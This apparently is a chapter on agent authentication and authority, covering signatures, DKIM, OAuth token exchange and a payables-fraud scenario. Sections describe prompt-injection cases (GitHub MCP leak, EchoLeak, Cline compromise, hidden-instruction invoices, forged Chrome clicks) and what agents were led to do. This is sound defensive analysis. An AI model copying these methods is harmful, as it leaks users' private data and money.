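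*Standing, Not Truth* (Louck, Dvir and Stulman, 2026) calls this kind of entitlement *standing* and tests what happens when agents ignore it. The researchers asked agents to choose between two software packages, each described by its own publisher. One publisher's description falsely stated that development of the rival package had stopped. The publisher used its own account and gave no instructions, so there was no impersonation or injected command to detect.

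In one set of 72 such choices, the agent picked the dishonest publisher's package every time. When the researchers added a valid signature, it still did so 69 times, and in half of the replies the model cited the signature as a reason to believe the claim. The signature showed who had published the package, but the publisher had no authority to say what its competitor was doing. When the researchers reworded every description as a statement by its publisher, a plain-English form of quoting, the agent again picked the dishonest publisher's package all 72 times. The agents repeated the attribution and then treated the claim as fact in their reasoning. The strongest labelling the researchers could devise cut the attack's success rate to 4.2%, but it disrupted more honest choices than deleting the sentence that made the claim.

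Across thirteen other models, the attack succeeded in 50.7% of decisions, with rates for individual models ranging from zero to nearly 100%.

Louck and colleagues propose accepting a claim if the speaker is also its subject, or if the platform has designated the speaker to make claims of that kind. A language model identifies whom each sentence is about, and the check then looks up whether the speaker may make that claim. It flagged all 72 dishonest descriptions, though this is weak evidence because the researchers had written them to be about a competitor. More usefully, it flagged only 6 of 645 pairings of real descriptions. Removing the flagged sentences and asking again stopped 130 of 131 attacks that had succeeded. When the researchers tried an attacker who knew how the check worked, most of the new wordings got past it, but they were so vague that they changed only 6 of 348 decisions.

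This is encouraging for package registries, which already know who published each entry. It helps the payables agent less, because the agent would have to know who wrote the email before it could apply the rule. A change of bank account is a claim about the supplier, so the rule would allow it only if the supplier had written the email.

### Acting on someone's behalf

Delegation is stronger than quoting. The logic writes "B for A" for B acting on A's behalf with A's agreement. Abadi and colleagues compare two ways for B to make such a request. In the simpler one, B sends the request with A's name attached, and the receiver has evidence that B quoted A but none that A appointed B. They consider this unsatisfactory in general. In the better one, A first signs a certificate stating that B serves A, and B presents it with each request:

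(B quoting A says r) and (B serves A) together give (B for A) says r

In the system Lampson and colleagues built, B must also accept the delegation, because both parties contribute their authority. The delegation expires after a short time, for example 30 minutes, unless A renews it.

This lets a program indicate whose authority it is using, which Hardy's compiler could not do. The supplier database could let "payables agent for records manager" change a bank account, but let "payables agent quoting supplier" only add a note for a human to read. If the fraudulent email led the agent to request a change, the request would go out in the supplier's name and the database would refuse it.

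The hard part is labelling the request correctly. Lampson and colleagues could assume that a program can identify whom it is quoting, and they set aside information flow. When an agent's model has read both the ticket and the manager's instructions and then requests a change to the record, the harness may be unable to determine which of the two prompted the request.

### A public issue on GitHub

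The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a widely used standard for connecting agents to tools. GitHub, a code host, offers an MCP server that lets an agent read and change its user's repositories, the folders that hold software projects. Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) describes an attack that the security company staged in May 2025 using demonstration repositories.

The user in the demonstration had several private repositories and a public one containing a Pac-Man game. Anyone can post an *issue*, such as a bug report, on a public repository, and the researchers posted one containing injected instructions. The user then asked Claude Desktop, running the Claude 4 Opus model, to look at the open issues. The agent read the issue, collected information from the private repositories and published it in a proposed change to the game. The leaked details included the name of a private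 project, the user's salary and a plan to move to South America.

GitHub was the relay, and the outsider who posted the issue was the author. The agent was properly connected to the user's GitHub account, and the server delivered the issue as posted. The agent could have got further than line 5 of the payables derivation, because GitHub is a good authority on which of its accounts posted an issue. The agent could fairly safely infer "this account says s" from "GitHub quoting this account says s". But the account had no right to give orders about the user's private files, and the agent acted as though the account spoke for the user.

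Invariant Labs found no fault in the server's code and concluded that GitHub could not fix the problem by patching the server. The company recommended continuous monitoring and a rule confining an agent to one repository per session. It sells products for both purposes, but the rule would have prevented this leak. Even under that rule, an injected issue could have misused the public repository. In a commentary also titled *GitHub MCP Exploited*, Willison pointed out that the server combined access to private data, exposure to outsiders' text and a way to send information out. He said he did not know the best fix.

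By default, Claude Desktop asked the user to confirm each use of a tool. According to Invariant Labs, many users switch to "Always Allow" and stop watching.

### EchoLeak in Microsoft 365 Copilot

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions using their email and files. In January 2025, researchers at Aim Labs found that an outsider could use it to steal confidential information by sending an employee one email. Reddy and Gujral (2025) reconstruct the attack in *EchoLeak*. When the employee later asked Copilot a question, its search could retrieve the outsider's email along with internal documents. The email then caused Copilot to put confidential details into its answer in a form that made the employee's software send them to the outsider, without the employee clicking on anything.

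The email passed through two relays, the company's mail system and the search component that placed it in the model's input. The email's author had no Copilot account and could not have questioned Copilot directly. The employee had signed in and was entitled to read the files. Copilot mistakenly treated the email as part of the employee's request.

Microsoft had a classifier to detect injected prompts, but the attackers' email was worded like an ordinary request to its human recipient. A genuine email would pose the same problem. A colleague may ask an employee to compile some files, and the employee may decline. The request becomes the employee's instruction to Copilot only if the employee chooses to pass it on.

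The attack also used a relay to send a request out. The employee's software would fetch images only from approved addresses, but a Microsoft Teams service on the approved list passed the request on to the attacker. The software had checked the relay's address but not the final destination.

Aim Labs demonstrated the attack without harming anyone. Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in May 2025, before it became public in June. SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration* reports a critical severity score of 9.3 and says that, according to Microsoft, nobody had exploited the flaw in the wild. Reddy and Gujral recommend keeping text from outside senders separate from the user's question and internal documents. They mention reports that Microsoft added options to stop Copilot from using external messages in some settings, though this leaves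 out some useful information.

### An issue title and 4,000 downloads

In February 2026 a similar weakness did cause harm. Cline is an AI coding tool whose developers used an AI bot to sort the issues on their GitHub repository. According to Willison (2026), in *6th March 2026*, the bot ran whenever a user opened an issue. It had permission to run commands, and its prompt included the issue's title. So Cline's own software put strangers' words in the same prompt as the developers' instructions.

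The security researcher Adnan Khan published the flaw on 9 February. Snyk's *How “Clinejection” Turned an AI Bot into a Supply Chain Attack* (2026) reports that an unknown person exploited it eight days later to release an unauthorised version of Cline on npm, a public registry where developers get software. The release installed OpenClaw, a separate AI agent, on their machines. *A GitHub Issue Title Compromised 4,000 Developer Machines* (2026) reports about 4,000 downloads, though some may have been repeat or automated. *Agent Compromised by Agent To Deploy an Agent* (2026) traces the intruder's first access to a single public issue. In a statement collected by the AI Incident Database, Khan says he tested the attack only on a copy of Cline's repository.

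GitHub, the first relay, correctly delivered an issue from one of its users, but the bot treated the issue's title as an order from Cline's developers. The second relay was npm. According to SafeDep's *AI Agent Cline v2.3.0 Compromised*, the intruder had obtained a token for publishing Cline's releases. npm accepted the token and passed the release on to developers, who had good reason to think it came from Cline. npm marked the version as deprecated after about eight hours, which ended the distribution. A lasting fix also has to keep outsiders' issue titles away from a bot that can run commands.

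### Fraudulent invoices and a forged click

The closest real parallel to the payables agent appeared in October 2026. *Prompt Injection Goes After the Inbox* (Trent, 2026) describes fraudulent invoices for around $88,000 that Sublime Security observed. Most of the recipients were financial controllers. The emails impersonated a cybersecurity company and contained invented messages from the target company's founders or chief executive. Invisible text carried further instructions for any AI agent that processed the inbox.

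In the logic, each invented message is a quotation inside a quotation, because the mail service quotes the sender, who quotes the chief executive. Even if the mail service delivers every word accurately, the chief executive may have said nothing. An agent that pays has assumed that a stranger reports the chief executive's orders reliably. As in the derivation, the remedy is an approval that reaches the agent by a separate route.

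Sublime Security's observations show that criminals are attempting this, but not that an agent has paid. Other companies have found similar attempts. Barracuda reported phishing emails aimed at both people and AI assistants (Mascellino, 2026, *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails*). In July, *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* (Mascellino, 2026) reported that Zscaler had found web pages with hidden text meant to make agents send cryptocurrency.

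Another attack from that month had a different cause. Claude for Chrome, a browser extension, can carry out nine built-in tasks when the user clicks on them. Constantin (2026), in *AI agent security*, reports Manifold Security's finding that the extension never checked whether a click was genuine. Any other extension in the browser could forge a click and make Claude read the user's Gmail, documents and calendar. If the user had turned on "Act without asking", Claude did this silently.

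Claude for Chrome treated every click as coming from the user, but other programs could also produce clicks. Checking the source of the forged click would have shown that it did not come from the user. No service was relaying someone else's words in this case.

### Would authentication have stopped these attacks?

In the case of the forged click, the agent should have authenticated its source. In the other cases, whether the agents should have done so depends on the hop, meaning one step between the author and the final action.

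| Case | Hop | What authentication showed or could have shown | Effect on the attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| GitHub MCP | Outsider to GitHub | Which account posted the issue | None, since anyone may post |
| GitHub MCP | GitHub to agent | That the issue came from GitHub | None, since it did |
| GitHub MCP | Agent to GitHub | That the agent was using its user's account | None, since it was |
| EchoLeak | Outsider to mailbox | At best, which outsider wrote | None, since outsiders may send email |
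| EchoLeak | Employee to Copilot | That the employee had signed in | None, since the employee had |
| Cline | Outsider to issue bot | Which account opened the issue | None, since anyone could start the bot |
| Cline | Intruder to npm | That the publishing token was valid | A token tied to Cline's release system might have helped |
| Invoice fraud | Sender to mailbox | Whether the message came from the chief executive's account | Could have exposed the impostor |
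| Claude for Chrome | Other extension to Claude | Nothing, because there was no check | A check would have stopped it |

Better authentication would have helped where the attacker was pretending to be someone else. It might have helped with Cline's release, although an intruder who had taken over the release system could have used even a well-protected key. In the GitHub and EchoLeak attacks, and at the start of the attack on Cline, the outsiders used a public form or an email address as its owner intended, so they didn't need to impersonate anyone. If GitHub had required a passport from everyone who opens an issue, the agent would still have leaked the same files, but to an identified person. Identification might have deterred some attackers and helped the police afterwards.

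A better argument for authentication is that rules about authority depend on it. "Take instructions only from the project's maintainers" is a sensible rule for an issue bot, and it would have blocked the title that started the attack on Cline. But the bot could apply the rule only if it could identify the account that opened each issue. GitHub had that information in both cases, and it later added filtering to its MCP server. A helpdesk that receives an email from an unfamiliar address has much less information about the sender to pass on.

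## Can a signature show who wrote a message after it has passed through several services?

A mutual TLS connection ends at each proxy and leaves the company with no evidence to show an outsider. A digital signature can instead travel with the message, so a receiver can check it after any number of services have handled the message, as long as none of them has changed the signed parts. How much the receiver learns about the author depends on whose key made the signature and what the key's holder meant by signing.

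### Signing a web request

Most services exchange messages over HTTP, the protocol of the web. An HTTP request has a method (POST, for example, submits data), a path, sometimes a query, named header lines and usually a body. Gateways routinely rewrite some of these, so a signature over the raw bytes would often fail verification even when nobody had tampered with the request.

*HTTP Message Signatures* (Backman, Richer and Sporny, 2024), an IETF standard also known as RFC 9421, avoids this problem by letting the signer choose which parts of a message to cover. The signer writes the names and values of those parts in a fixed layout, called the *signature base*, and signs that. The receiver rebuilds the signature base from the message it received and checks the signature against it.

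The standard leaves the choice of parts to each application. Salowey and Sheffer (2026), in *WIMSE Workload-to-Workload Authentication with HTTP Signatures*, make that choice for requests between programs, in a draft for the IETF's WIMSE group. Under their rules, the helpdesk's request to the payables agent might look like this, with the long strings shortened:

```
POST /tickets?queue=suppliers HTTP/1.1
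Host: payables.example.com
Content-Type: application/json
Content-Digest: sha-256=:mR4k...:
Workload-Identity-Token: eyJh...
Signature-Input: sig1=("@method" "@path" "@query" "content-type"
    "content-digest" "workload-identity-token");
    created=1796472000;expires=1796472120;nonce="Zk3vQ9...";
    tag="wimse-workload-to-workload";
    wimse-aud="https://payables.example.com/tickets"
Signature: sig1=:p8Xd...:

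{"from":"accounts@supplier.example","text":"Our bank account is now 4471."}
```

The *Workload Identity Token* is a signed statement that ties the helpdesk's name to a public key. `Content-Digest` is a hash of the body. The two times are in seconds and are two minutes apart. From all this the helpdesk builds the signature base:

```
"@method": POST
"@path": /tickets
"@query": ?queue=suppliers
"content-type": application/json
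"content-digest": sha-256=:mR4k...:
"workload-identity-token": eyJh...
"@signature-params": (the list of parts, times, nonce, tag and audience)
```

It then uses its private key k to compute signature = Sign(k, signature base). The last line of the base protects the signature's own conditions, so nobody can extend the expiry time without making the signature invalid.

A gateway between the helpdesk and the agent could do the following:

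| Change by the gateway | Does the request still pass? | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Replaces the host name with an internal one | Yes | The signature doesn't cover the host. |
| Reorders the headers or adds a note of the route taken | Yes | Neither affects the signature base. |
| Moves the ticket to another queue | No | The signature covers the query. |
| Changes 4471 to 9902 in the body | No | The body no longer matches its digest. |
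| Compresses the body | No | The digest depends on the encoding. |
| Adds a header reading "Approved-By: records-manager" | Yes | The signature doesn't cover the new header. |

The signature covers the digest header and not the body, so it would remain valid after the account number was changed. To catch the change, the harness has to verify the signature, compute the digest of the body it received, and compare that digest with the one in the header.

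The added approval is more dangerous, because the request still passes the check and now contains a false statement. Backman and colleagues recommend that receivers trust only the signed parts, and suggest removing sensitive unsigned parts before processing the rest. They also recommend testing with bad signatures. A program that ignores the result of the check would still pass every test that uses good ones.

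Sometimes a gateway has to change a signed part of a message. It can check the helpdesk's signature, make the change and add its own signature, but the agent then usually has to rely on the gateway's check of the original signature. Salowey and Sheffer point out that re-signing authenticates the intermediary instead of the original program. In the notation of the previous section, "helpdesk says m" becomes "gateway says (helpdesk says m)".

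### Audience, time and single use

Gateways that decrypt traffic can see the whole signed request and could send it again or to somewhere else. The draft limits this in three ways.

The `wimse-aud` value names the intended recipient. The harness compares it, character by character, with a list an administrator has configured. It must not take the expected value from the request's host header, because an attacker could set that header to match. The expiry time should be minutes away. The *nonce*, a value with at least 64 bits of randomness, lets the harness recognise a request it has already accepted.

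But the draft makes it optional to remember nonces, and does not require different copies of a service to share the ones they have seen. If the company runs three copies of the payables agent, a malicious gateway could deliver the same ticket to each of them within the two minutes, and all three might accept it. Salowey and Sheffer therefore do not list replay protection among the draft's security goals. A duplicate ticket is only a nuisance, but to prevent duplicate payments the company would need a further safeguard, such as a shared database that blocks a second payment for the same invoice number.

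A gateway could also discard the ticket and invent a reply. To prevent this, the helpdesk can require a signed response containing the nonce from its request and treat anything else as a failure.

Campbell and Schwenkschuster's *WIMSE Workload Proof Token* (2026) describes the WIMSE group's simpler alternative. The calling program signs a small separate token and sends it with the request. This token contains the audience, an expiry time, a unique identifier and a hash of the program's identity token. According to an earlier version of the draft, the IETF's *WIMSE Workload-Proof-Token* (2026), the signed token should expire within minutes or seconds, and 128 random bits are enough to make the identifier unique.

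The proof token doesn't cover the body, so a gateway could replace the words "do stuff" in the draft's sample request with any others while the proof remained valid. Campbell and Schwenkschuster accept that the token offers no protection against an actively malicious intermediary. But it isn't tied to HTTP, so it also suits systems that pass messages through queues. The full signature is the better choice for a ticket that contains a bank account number.

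A full signature also settles part of the dispute over what a ticket contained. The company can show an outsider the signed request, the identity token and the issuer's public key, and it could not have produced the request itself because it doesn't have the helpdesk's private key. (RFC 9421 also permits checksums made with a shared key, which would not prove this.) But the signature shows only that the helpdesk sent a ticket with the supplier's name in it, so evidence about the supplier has to come from an earlier point on the route.

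### What email signatures cover

Email has had signatures that travel with the message for almost twenty years. The IETF first standardised DomainKeys Identified Mail (DKIM) in 2007. When the supplier's bookkeeper sends an email, the supplier's mail server adds a header such as this one:

```
DKIM-Signature: v=1; a=rsa-sha256; d=supplier.example; s=mail2026;
    h=from:to:subject:date; bh=Qw7e...; b=Lx2f...
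```

Here `d` is the domain that takes responsibility for the message, `bh` is a hash of the body, `b` is the signature, and `h` lists the headers that the signature covers, which must include the "From" line. The receiving server uses `s` and `d` to form an address in the domain name system (DNS), the internet's public directory of names, and looks up the supplier's public key there. It then recomputes the body hash and checks the signature.

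The key belongs to the mail server, which normally uses it for everyone with an account in the domain. A valid signature therefore shows that supplier.example accepted responsibility for the message, but not which employee wrote it. DKIM has an optional field for a more specific identity, but the domain decides what to put there. The display name beside the address is even weaker evidence, because a stranger can open a free account, set the name to "Supplier Ltd Accounts" and receive a valid signature from the provider.

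S/MIME and OpenPGP let individuals sign their own emails. The bookkeeper can sign with a personal key before the message reaches any server. Few suppliers use these signatures, since each correspondent has to obtain and look after a key.

### How forwarding breaks them

Simple forwarding leaves a DKIM signature intact. A mailing list that puts its name in the subject line or adds a footer changes the signed content, so the signature check fails. The receiving server can't easily distinguish these edits from tampering.

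The Authenticated Received Chain (ARC), an experimental protocol from 2019, is meant to preserve the results of checks made before a message was changed. The forwarder checks the message before changing it and records the results in a new header. It then signs the changed message and seals the whole set of ARC headers, including those from earlier forwarders. The final recipient can read the mailing list's record that the email arrived with a valid signature from supplier.example.

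The recipient still can't check that signature, and has to decide whether to believe the mailing list. A dishonest forwarder could make up an email, attach a report that supplier.example had signed it, and add ARC signatures that are all valid. To accept the report, the recipient has to assume that the list reliably reports what others said, as the payables agent had to assume about the helpdesk.

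DKIM also doesn't prevent someone from resending a signed message to more people, because the signature doesn't cover the *envelope*, the delivery instructions that mail servers exchange separately from the visible "To" line. A spammer can send one email to themselves through a reputable provider, then send the signed copy to thousands of other addresses. The IETF's *DKIM2 Deployment Profile* (2026) lists such replays among the limitations that DKIM2, a proposed successor, is meant to address.

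Clayton, Chuang and Gondwana (2026) set out the new design in *DomainKeys Identified Mail Signatures v2 (DKIM2)*, in which each domain that handles a message signs it together with details of its transmission. An October 2025 version by Clayton and colleagues describes how these signatures form a chain from author to recipient. The wider design also has forwarders record how to undo their changes, so that a recipient can reconstruct the earlier text and check its signature. This would improve on ARC when forwarders add footers or change subject lines. DKIM2 identifies domains, as DKIM does, and was still a working-group draft in November 2026.

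### DKIM and the supplier's email

Suppose the helpdesk checks DKIM on every email that it turns into a ticket. The result depends on who sent the request to use account 4471:

| Who sent the email | What the check finds |
|---|---|
| The supplier's bookkeeper | A valid signature from supplier.example |
| An intruder in the bookkeeper's mailbox | A valid signature from supplier.example |
| A stranger who registered supplier-billing.example | A valid signature from supplier-billing.example |
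| A stranger with a free account in the supplier's name | A valid signature from the free provider |
| A stranger who forged the supplier's address | No valid signature from supplier.example |
| The bookkeeper, through a list that adds a footer | A broken signature |

If the company has the supplier's correct domain on file and requires a match, the check catches all three strangers, which is enough to make it worth having. It can't catch the intruder, whose email has the same signature as an honest one, and it wrongly flags the bookkeeper's email from the list.

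The helpdesk also breaks the signature when it copies the email's text into a ticket. The payables agent could repeat the check only if the helpdesk attached the original email unchanged and the supplier's public key was still in DNS. Domain owners replace their keys from time to time, so the agent or the harness should check the signature on arrival and keep the key with the result.

### Signed agent cards

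The supplier might instead have its own agent, which contacts the company's agent directly. Agent2Agent (A2A), a protocol that Google introduced in 2025 and later handed to the Linux Foundation, is meant for such cases. An A2A agent publishes an *agent card*, a file that gives its name, web address, the tasks it can perform and how other programs can authenticate to it.

The card's publisher can sign it. The signing program puts the card into a standard form, so that differences in spacing or order don't matter, and then attaches a signature. If the company finds the supplier's card in a third party's directory, it can use the signature to check that the directory hasn't replaced the supplier's web address with a fraudster's. The company needs a trustworthy way to find the supplier's public key, because a fraudster could sign a false card with a different key.

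The signature covers only the card, not the messages the agent later sends. A2A leaves authenticating messages to ordinary web methods such as mutual TLS and OAuth. So a valid card gives the payables agent no reason to believe a message about account 4471, unless the message has its own link to the supplier.

The card's contents are also the publisher's claims about its own product. A signature can show that the publisher described its agent as careful with invoices, but not that the description is true. A client's model may read the description when it chooses an agent, so a dishonest publisher could insert instructions in it. Louck and colleagues found the same weakness with software packages, where models cited a valid signature as a reason to believe a false description.

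### Signing every action

Rajagopalan and Rao (2026), in *Authenticated Workflows*, apply signatures to an agent's actions as well as its messages. Rajagopalan works at MACAW Security, a company in this field. They give every agent and every tool its own key pair, and a component at each boundary refuses any call without a valid signature. A call has the form

Invocation = (Args, Policy, MAC), where MAC = Sign(K, Args ‖ Policy)

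*Args* are the details of the requested action, such as a supplier's number and a new bank account. *Policy* identifies the rules that apply to it, and K is the caller's key. Before a tool runs, the checking component does three things:

1. It verifies the signature with the caller's registered public key.
2. It confirms that nobody has substituted a different policy.
3. It evaluates the request against the policy.

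The company's rules and the tool's own rules both apply, so an action is permitted only if both permit it, and forbidden if either forbids it. Adding another policy can therefore only reduce what the agent may do. Policies can also require *attestations*, which are signed statements that an earlier step has finished. For example, a company could allow an export of customer data only after a signed statement that another program has anonymised the data.

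Rajagopalan and Rao report that the system blocked every attack in 174 test cases and produced no false positives. The cases came from 11 attack patterns, repeated across different agent frameworks and configurations. The researchers also reconstructed two publicised attacks, on OpenAI's Atlas browser and on GitHub's MCP server, and the system blocked both. Signing took about 0.1 milliseconds, and checking a signature took slightly less. The whole check on a local tool took under a millisecond, although an optional review by a language model added 150 to 500 milliseconds.

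The low overhead removes a common excuse for leaving calls unsigned. The perfect score is harder to interpret. Rajagopalan and Rao classify ten of their 11 attack patterns, including prompt injection, as blocked by policy. Cryptography alone stopped only session fixation, in which an attacker tricks someone into using a session the attacker controls. Yet they write that an attack would require breaking cryptography, "not crafting clever prompts".

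One of their own examples shows why. A poisoned document causes the model to request a file of credentials. The agent's software signs the request as usual, so the signature is valid, and the tool rejects the request only because a rule forbids files with "credential" in the name. The attack would have worked on a sensitive file that had an ordinary name and that the policy allowed.

The GitHub test has a similar limitation. In the researchers' version, the injected issue made an agent use filesystem tools to look for credentials, and rules about credentials blocked the attempt. A ban on credential files would not have prevented the leak that Invariant Labs demonstrated, in which the agent used ordinary GitHub tools to publish private project details.

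Their formal guarantee explicitly assumes that attackers can't forge signatures, that the central services holding keys and policies are trustworthy, and that agents can't bypass the checking components. The company also has to supply suitable policies. A rule that lets the payables agent edit supplier records would still let the fraudulent change through. Requiring an attestation from the records manager would prevent this, provided that the attestation named the account. Otherwise, an approval for one supplier might allow a change for another.

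### Purchase mandates signed by the user

In Authenticated Workflows, software usually signs a call after the model has composed it, so the signature authenticates the model's output. The Agent Payments Protocol (AP2), which Google announced in September 2025 with a group of payment companies and merchants, instead has the user sign records called *mandates*.

In AP2 as announced, when the user is present, the agent assembles a shopping cart and the merchant signs its contents and price. The user then approves the purchase on a trusted device, which signs a hash of the cart and the payment details. If the agent adds a gift card afterwards, the cart no longer matches the signed hash, and the merchant or payment provider can refuse the purchase. The bank or card network also receives a separate payment mandate showing that an agent was involved.

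When the user is away, there may be no cart to approve, so the user signs an *intent mandate* beforehand. It describes the purchase in ordinary language and sets limits such as an expiry time and the permitted merchants. The agent can later buy within those limits. Ordinary software can check whether a merchant is on the list, but a model may have to decide whether a pair of shoes counts as "comfortable for long walks". An injected product review could influence that decision without invalidating the user's signature.

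AP2 is a specification, so the argument for it is based on its design rather than on measured attack rates. It relies on the user's device to keep the key safe and to display exactly what it signs. The merchant and the payment provider have to reject purchases without a valid mandate, and the user has to read the screen. A hostile seller may still persuade the agent to put a poor product in the cart. If the user then approves the purchase without looking closely, the mandate becomes evidence that the user wanted that product.

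Despite these weaknesses, AP2 seems to put the signature in a better place for consequential actions. The company could do the same for supplier records by having its records manager sign a short statement giving the supplier's number, the new account number, an expiry time and a unique number for the change. The harness would check the statement and pass the account number straight to the database, so the model could propose a change but couldn't alter an approved one.

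### Summaries, translations and unsigned text

The payables agent may never see the supplier's exact words, because the helpdesk might translate an email from German or shorten a long exchange to three sentences. A signature on the original doesn't cover the new version, and a record of changes, like the one DKIM2 keeps, couldn't be used to reconstruct the original email from a summary.

The service can keep the signed original beside the summary. The agent's model can then read the summary while ordinary code takes the account number from the original. This works for a number in a predictable place, but less well for a condition in the middle of a paragraph, such as "use the new account only for invoices from March". The summarising program can also sign its output along with a hash of the original. A receiver can then check which program wrote the summary and from what text, but must still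 trust that the program summarised it accurately.

A larger difficulty is that most of what agents read, such as web pages, product reviews and scanned letters, isn't signed by its author. An agent that ignored all of it would be of little use. The usual response is to let the agent use unsigned text as information but never as authorisation. Fewer people then need signing keys. The company can't give keys to everyone who might email it, but it can give them to the ten employees who approve changes.

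That division is sensible for orders, but it protects less against false information. An unsigned remark about a frozen bank account could still lead the agent to recommend a change, and the records manager might sign it in good faith unless the company also required a phone call to the supplier.

### Stolen keys

If a thief copies the manager's key, a receiver can't tell the thief's approvals from the manager's. Short-lived keys and rapid cancellation limit the damage. A company can also keep the key in a security chip that makes signatures without releasing it, and require a fingerprint or PIN for each signature.

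These measures make the signing key harder to copy but don't prevent all misuse. Malware on the manager's computer could show one account number and send another to the chip, which would sign it. A separate device with its own screen gives better protection because the manager can compare the account number it shows with the one on the computer.

A company that cancels a stolen key must also decide which past signatures to trust. The signer sets the creation time in an HTTP signature, so a thief could backdate it to before the theft. A receiver that recorded when each approval arrived could reject those that arrived after the theft, but the company would still need to estimate when the theft occurred.

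### Valid signatures on hostile messages

A fraudster can own a domain, publish a DKIM key and sign every fraudulent email correctly. A fraudster can also have a validly signed agent card, and an ordinary customer's signatures remain valid if the customer turns hostile. The cryptography works as intended in all these cases, because it is designed only to identify a key and protect the signed content.

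The company can still base rules on the signer's name, such as refusing messages signed by domains it doesn't recognise or blocking a supplier's key after one fraud. An unknown signer who is blocked can return under another name, so a list of permitted signers is more useful than a list of banned ones. Neither list would stop the intruder in the bookkeeper's mailbox.

A receiver must also check that the signer is the right one for the request. Backman and colleagues warn that an attacker can add their own valid signature to someone else's message. A harness that checked only for a valid signature would accept a change of bank details signed by a stranger. The harness, not the model, should apply a rule for this check, and the rule must name the expected key holder and the action that person may approve.

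## How do access tokens record on whose behalf an agent acts?

A records manager can sign a handful of bank account changes a week, but nobody would sign each of the hundreds of requests an agent may make in a day. Companies therefore usually give an agent standing permission through a delegation token, a signed credential that lets one party act for another within stated limits. The most common system for issuing these tokens is OAuth, which lets people give a program limited access to their accounts without sharing their password. Anyone who has let a scheduling app read their calendar has probably used OAuth.

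### How OAuth delegates access

Suppose the payables agent needs to edit the supplier database on behalf of the records manager. The company runs an *authorisation server*, which logs people in and issues tokens. Kasselman and colleagues recommend the following sequence for an agent that acts for a user:

1. The harness sends the records manager's browser to the authorisation server with a list of the permissions it wants.
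2. The records manager logs in there and approves the list.
3. The server sends a code back to the harness through the browser.
4. The harness proves its own identity to the server, for example with its SPIFFE credential, and trades the code for an *access token*.
5. The harness attaches the access token to each request it sends to the database.

Many access tokens are JSON Web Tokens (JWTs), which are short lists of named values with the issuer's signature. OAuth calls these values *claims*. Four of them matter most here:

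- `sub`, the subject, is the user whose rights the request would use.
- `client_id` is the program that obtained the token.
- `aud`, the audience, is the service that should accept the token.
- `scope` lists the kinds of action that the token permits.

The database can determine from these claims that the payables agent is calling and using the records manager's rights. No claim identifies who wrote the text that led the agent to make the request.

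An agent can also obtain a token on its own behalf, without any user taking part. A payables agent that starts work whenever a ticket arrives might well do this, and its token would then not identify any person.

Kasselman and colleagues also allow an agent to be the protected service, so that other programs need a token to call it. If a support employee escalated a ticket, the helpdesk could present a token with that employee as its subject, and the payables agent would have good evidence of who was asking. This doesn't work for the supplier's email, because the bookkeeper has never logged in to the company's authorisation server. The helpdesk can therefore only present a token for itself.

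### Exchanging one token for another

Agents often reach a service through a tool. Suppose the payables agent calls a banking tool, which checks that an account number is well formed and then writes it to the supplier database. The token the tool received has the tool as its audience, so the tool needs a different token for the database.

*OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange* (RFC 8693), an IETF standard by Jones, Nadalin and colleagues, defines how the banking tool can get a new token. The tool sends the authorisation server the token it received, as the `subject_token`, and a token that identifies the tool, as the `actor_token`. It also names the service it needs to call. The server checks the request against its policy and issues the new token.

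The new token can follow either of two models. Under *impersonation*, it identifies only the records manager, and the database cannot distinguish the tool from the manager. Under *delegation*, it identifies both, with the acting program in a claim called `act`. When a request has passed through several programs, each `act` claim can contain an earlier one. A token for the chain from records manager to payables agent to banking tool might contain the following claims:

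```
{
  "iss": "https://auth.example.com",
  "aud": "https://suppliers.example.com",
  "iat": 1796472000,
  "exp": 1796472300,
  "sub": "records.manager@example.com",
  "client_id": "banking-tool",
  "scope": "suppliers.bank-details.write",
  "act": {
    "sub": "spiffe://example.com/finance/banking-tool",
    "act": {
      "sub": "spiffe://example.com/finance/payables-agent"
    }
  }
}
```

| Claim | What the database can read from it |
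|---|---|
| `iss` | The company's authorisation server issued the token. |
| `aud` | The token is for the supplier database and no other service. |
| `iat` and `exp` | The server issued it at noon UTC on 5 December 2026, and it expires five minutes later. |
| `sub` | The request uses the records manager's rights. |
| `client_id` | The banking tool obtained this token. |
| `scope` | The holder may change suppliers' bank details. |
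| Outer `act` | The banking tool is the program acting now. |
| Inner `act` | The payables agent acted before it. |

The payables agent was the client in the first token but appears only in the inner `act` claim of the second. Jones and colleagues require the database to base its decision only on the top-level claims and the current actor. Earlier actors, such as the payables agent, are "informational only". The company may want a second approval when an agent uses the banking tool, but not when the records manager uses it directly. The standard doesn't let the database base that rule on the inner claim, but the authorisation server could still apply it when the tool requests the exchange, because the server receives the incoming token.

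The history is also only as complete as the server makes it. *Cryptographically Verifiable Actor Chains for OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange* (Prasad, Krishnan and colleagues, 2026) says that RFC 8693 has no common rules for preserving and checking a delegation path through repeated exchanges. The draft proposes six ways to do so, which differ in how much of the path they disclose. *OAuth Actor Profile for Delegation* (McGuinness, 2026) finds that different kinds of token also represent the acting agent inconsistently. For now, two companies that follow the standard may produce quite different records of the same chain.

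Withdrawing permission is another weak point, because an exchange happens once and doesn't link the new token to the old one. If the records manager cancels the agent's access at 12:01, the banking tool's token may remain valid until 12:05 unless the company has built its own way to pass on the cancellation.

### Transaction tokens

A request to the supplier database may pass through several internal programs, one to check it, one to write the record and perhaps another to notify the accounts team. If these programs all passed along the same access token, an intruder who found it in any of their logs could use it to make a different change.

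Tulshibagwale, Fletcher and Kasselman (2026), in *Transaction Tokens*, address this with a token for a single transaction. The first program to receive the request exchanges the access token for a transaction token, and the others pass it along unchanged. It lasts minutes at most and works only inside the company's own trust domain. Its scope can be no wider than that of the original token. It also contains details of the transaction, which for the change of bank account might be:

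```
"txn": "5f0c7a...",
"req_wl": "supplier-gateway",
"scope": "change-bank-account",
"tctx": { "supplier": "2207", "new_account": "4471" }
```

Here `txn` is a unique number for the transaction, `req_wl` identifies the program that asked for the token, and `tctx` holds the details that must not change during the transaction. If an intruder took over the checking program and changed 4471 to 9902, the program that writes the record could compare the request with the token and refuse the request. Someone could still replay the unaltered token before it expires, unless the services keep a shared record of the transaction numbers they have seen.

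This improves on passing an ordinary access token around, because the signature covers the account number as well as a general permission. But the token service bases `tctx` on information from the requesting program. If a fraudulent email led the agent to ask for account 4471, the token would protect that number from alteration all the way to the database.

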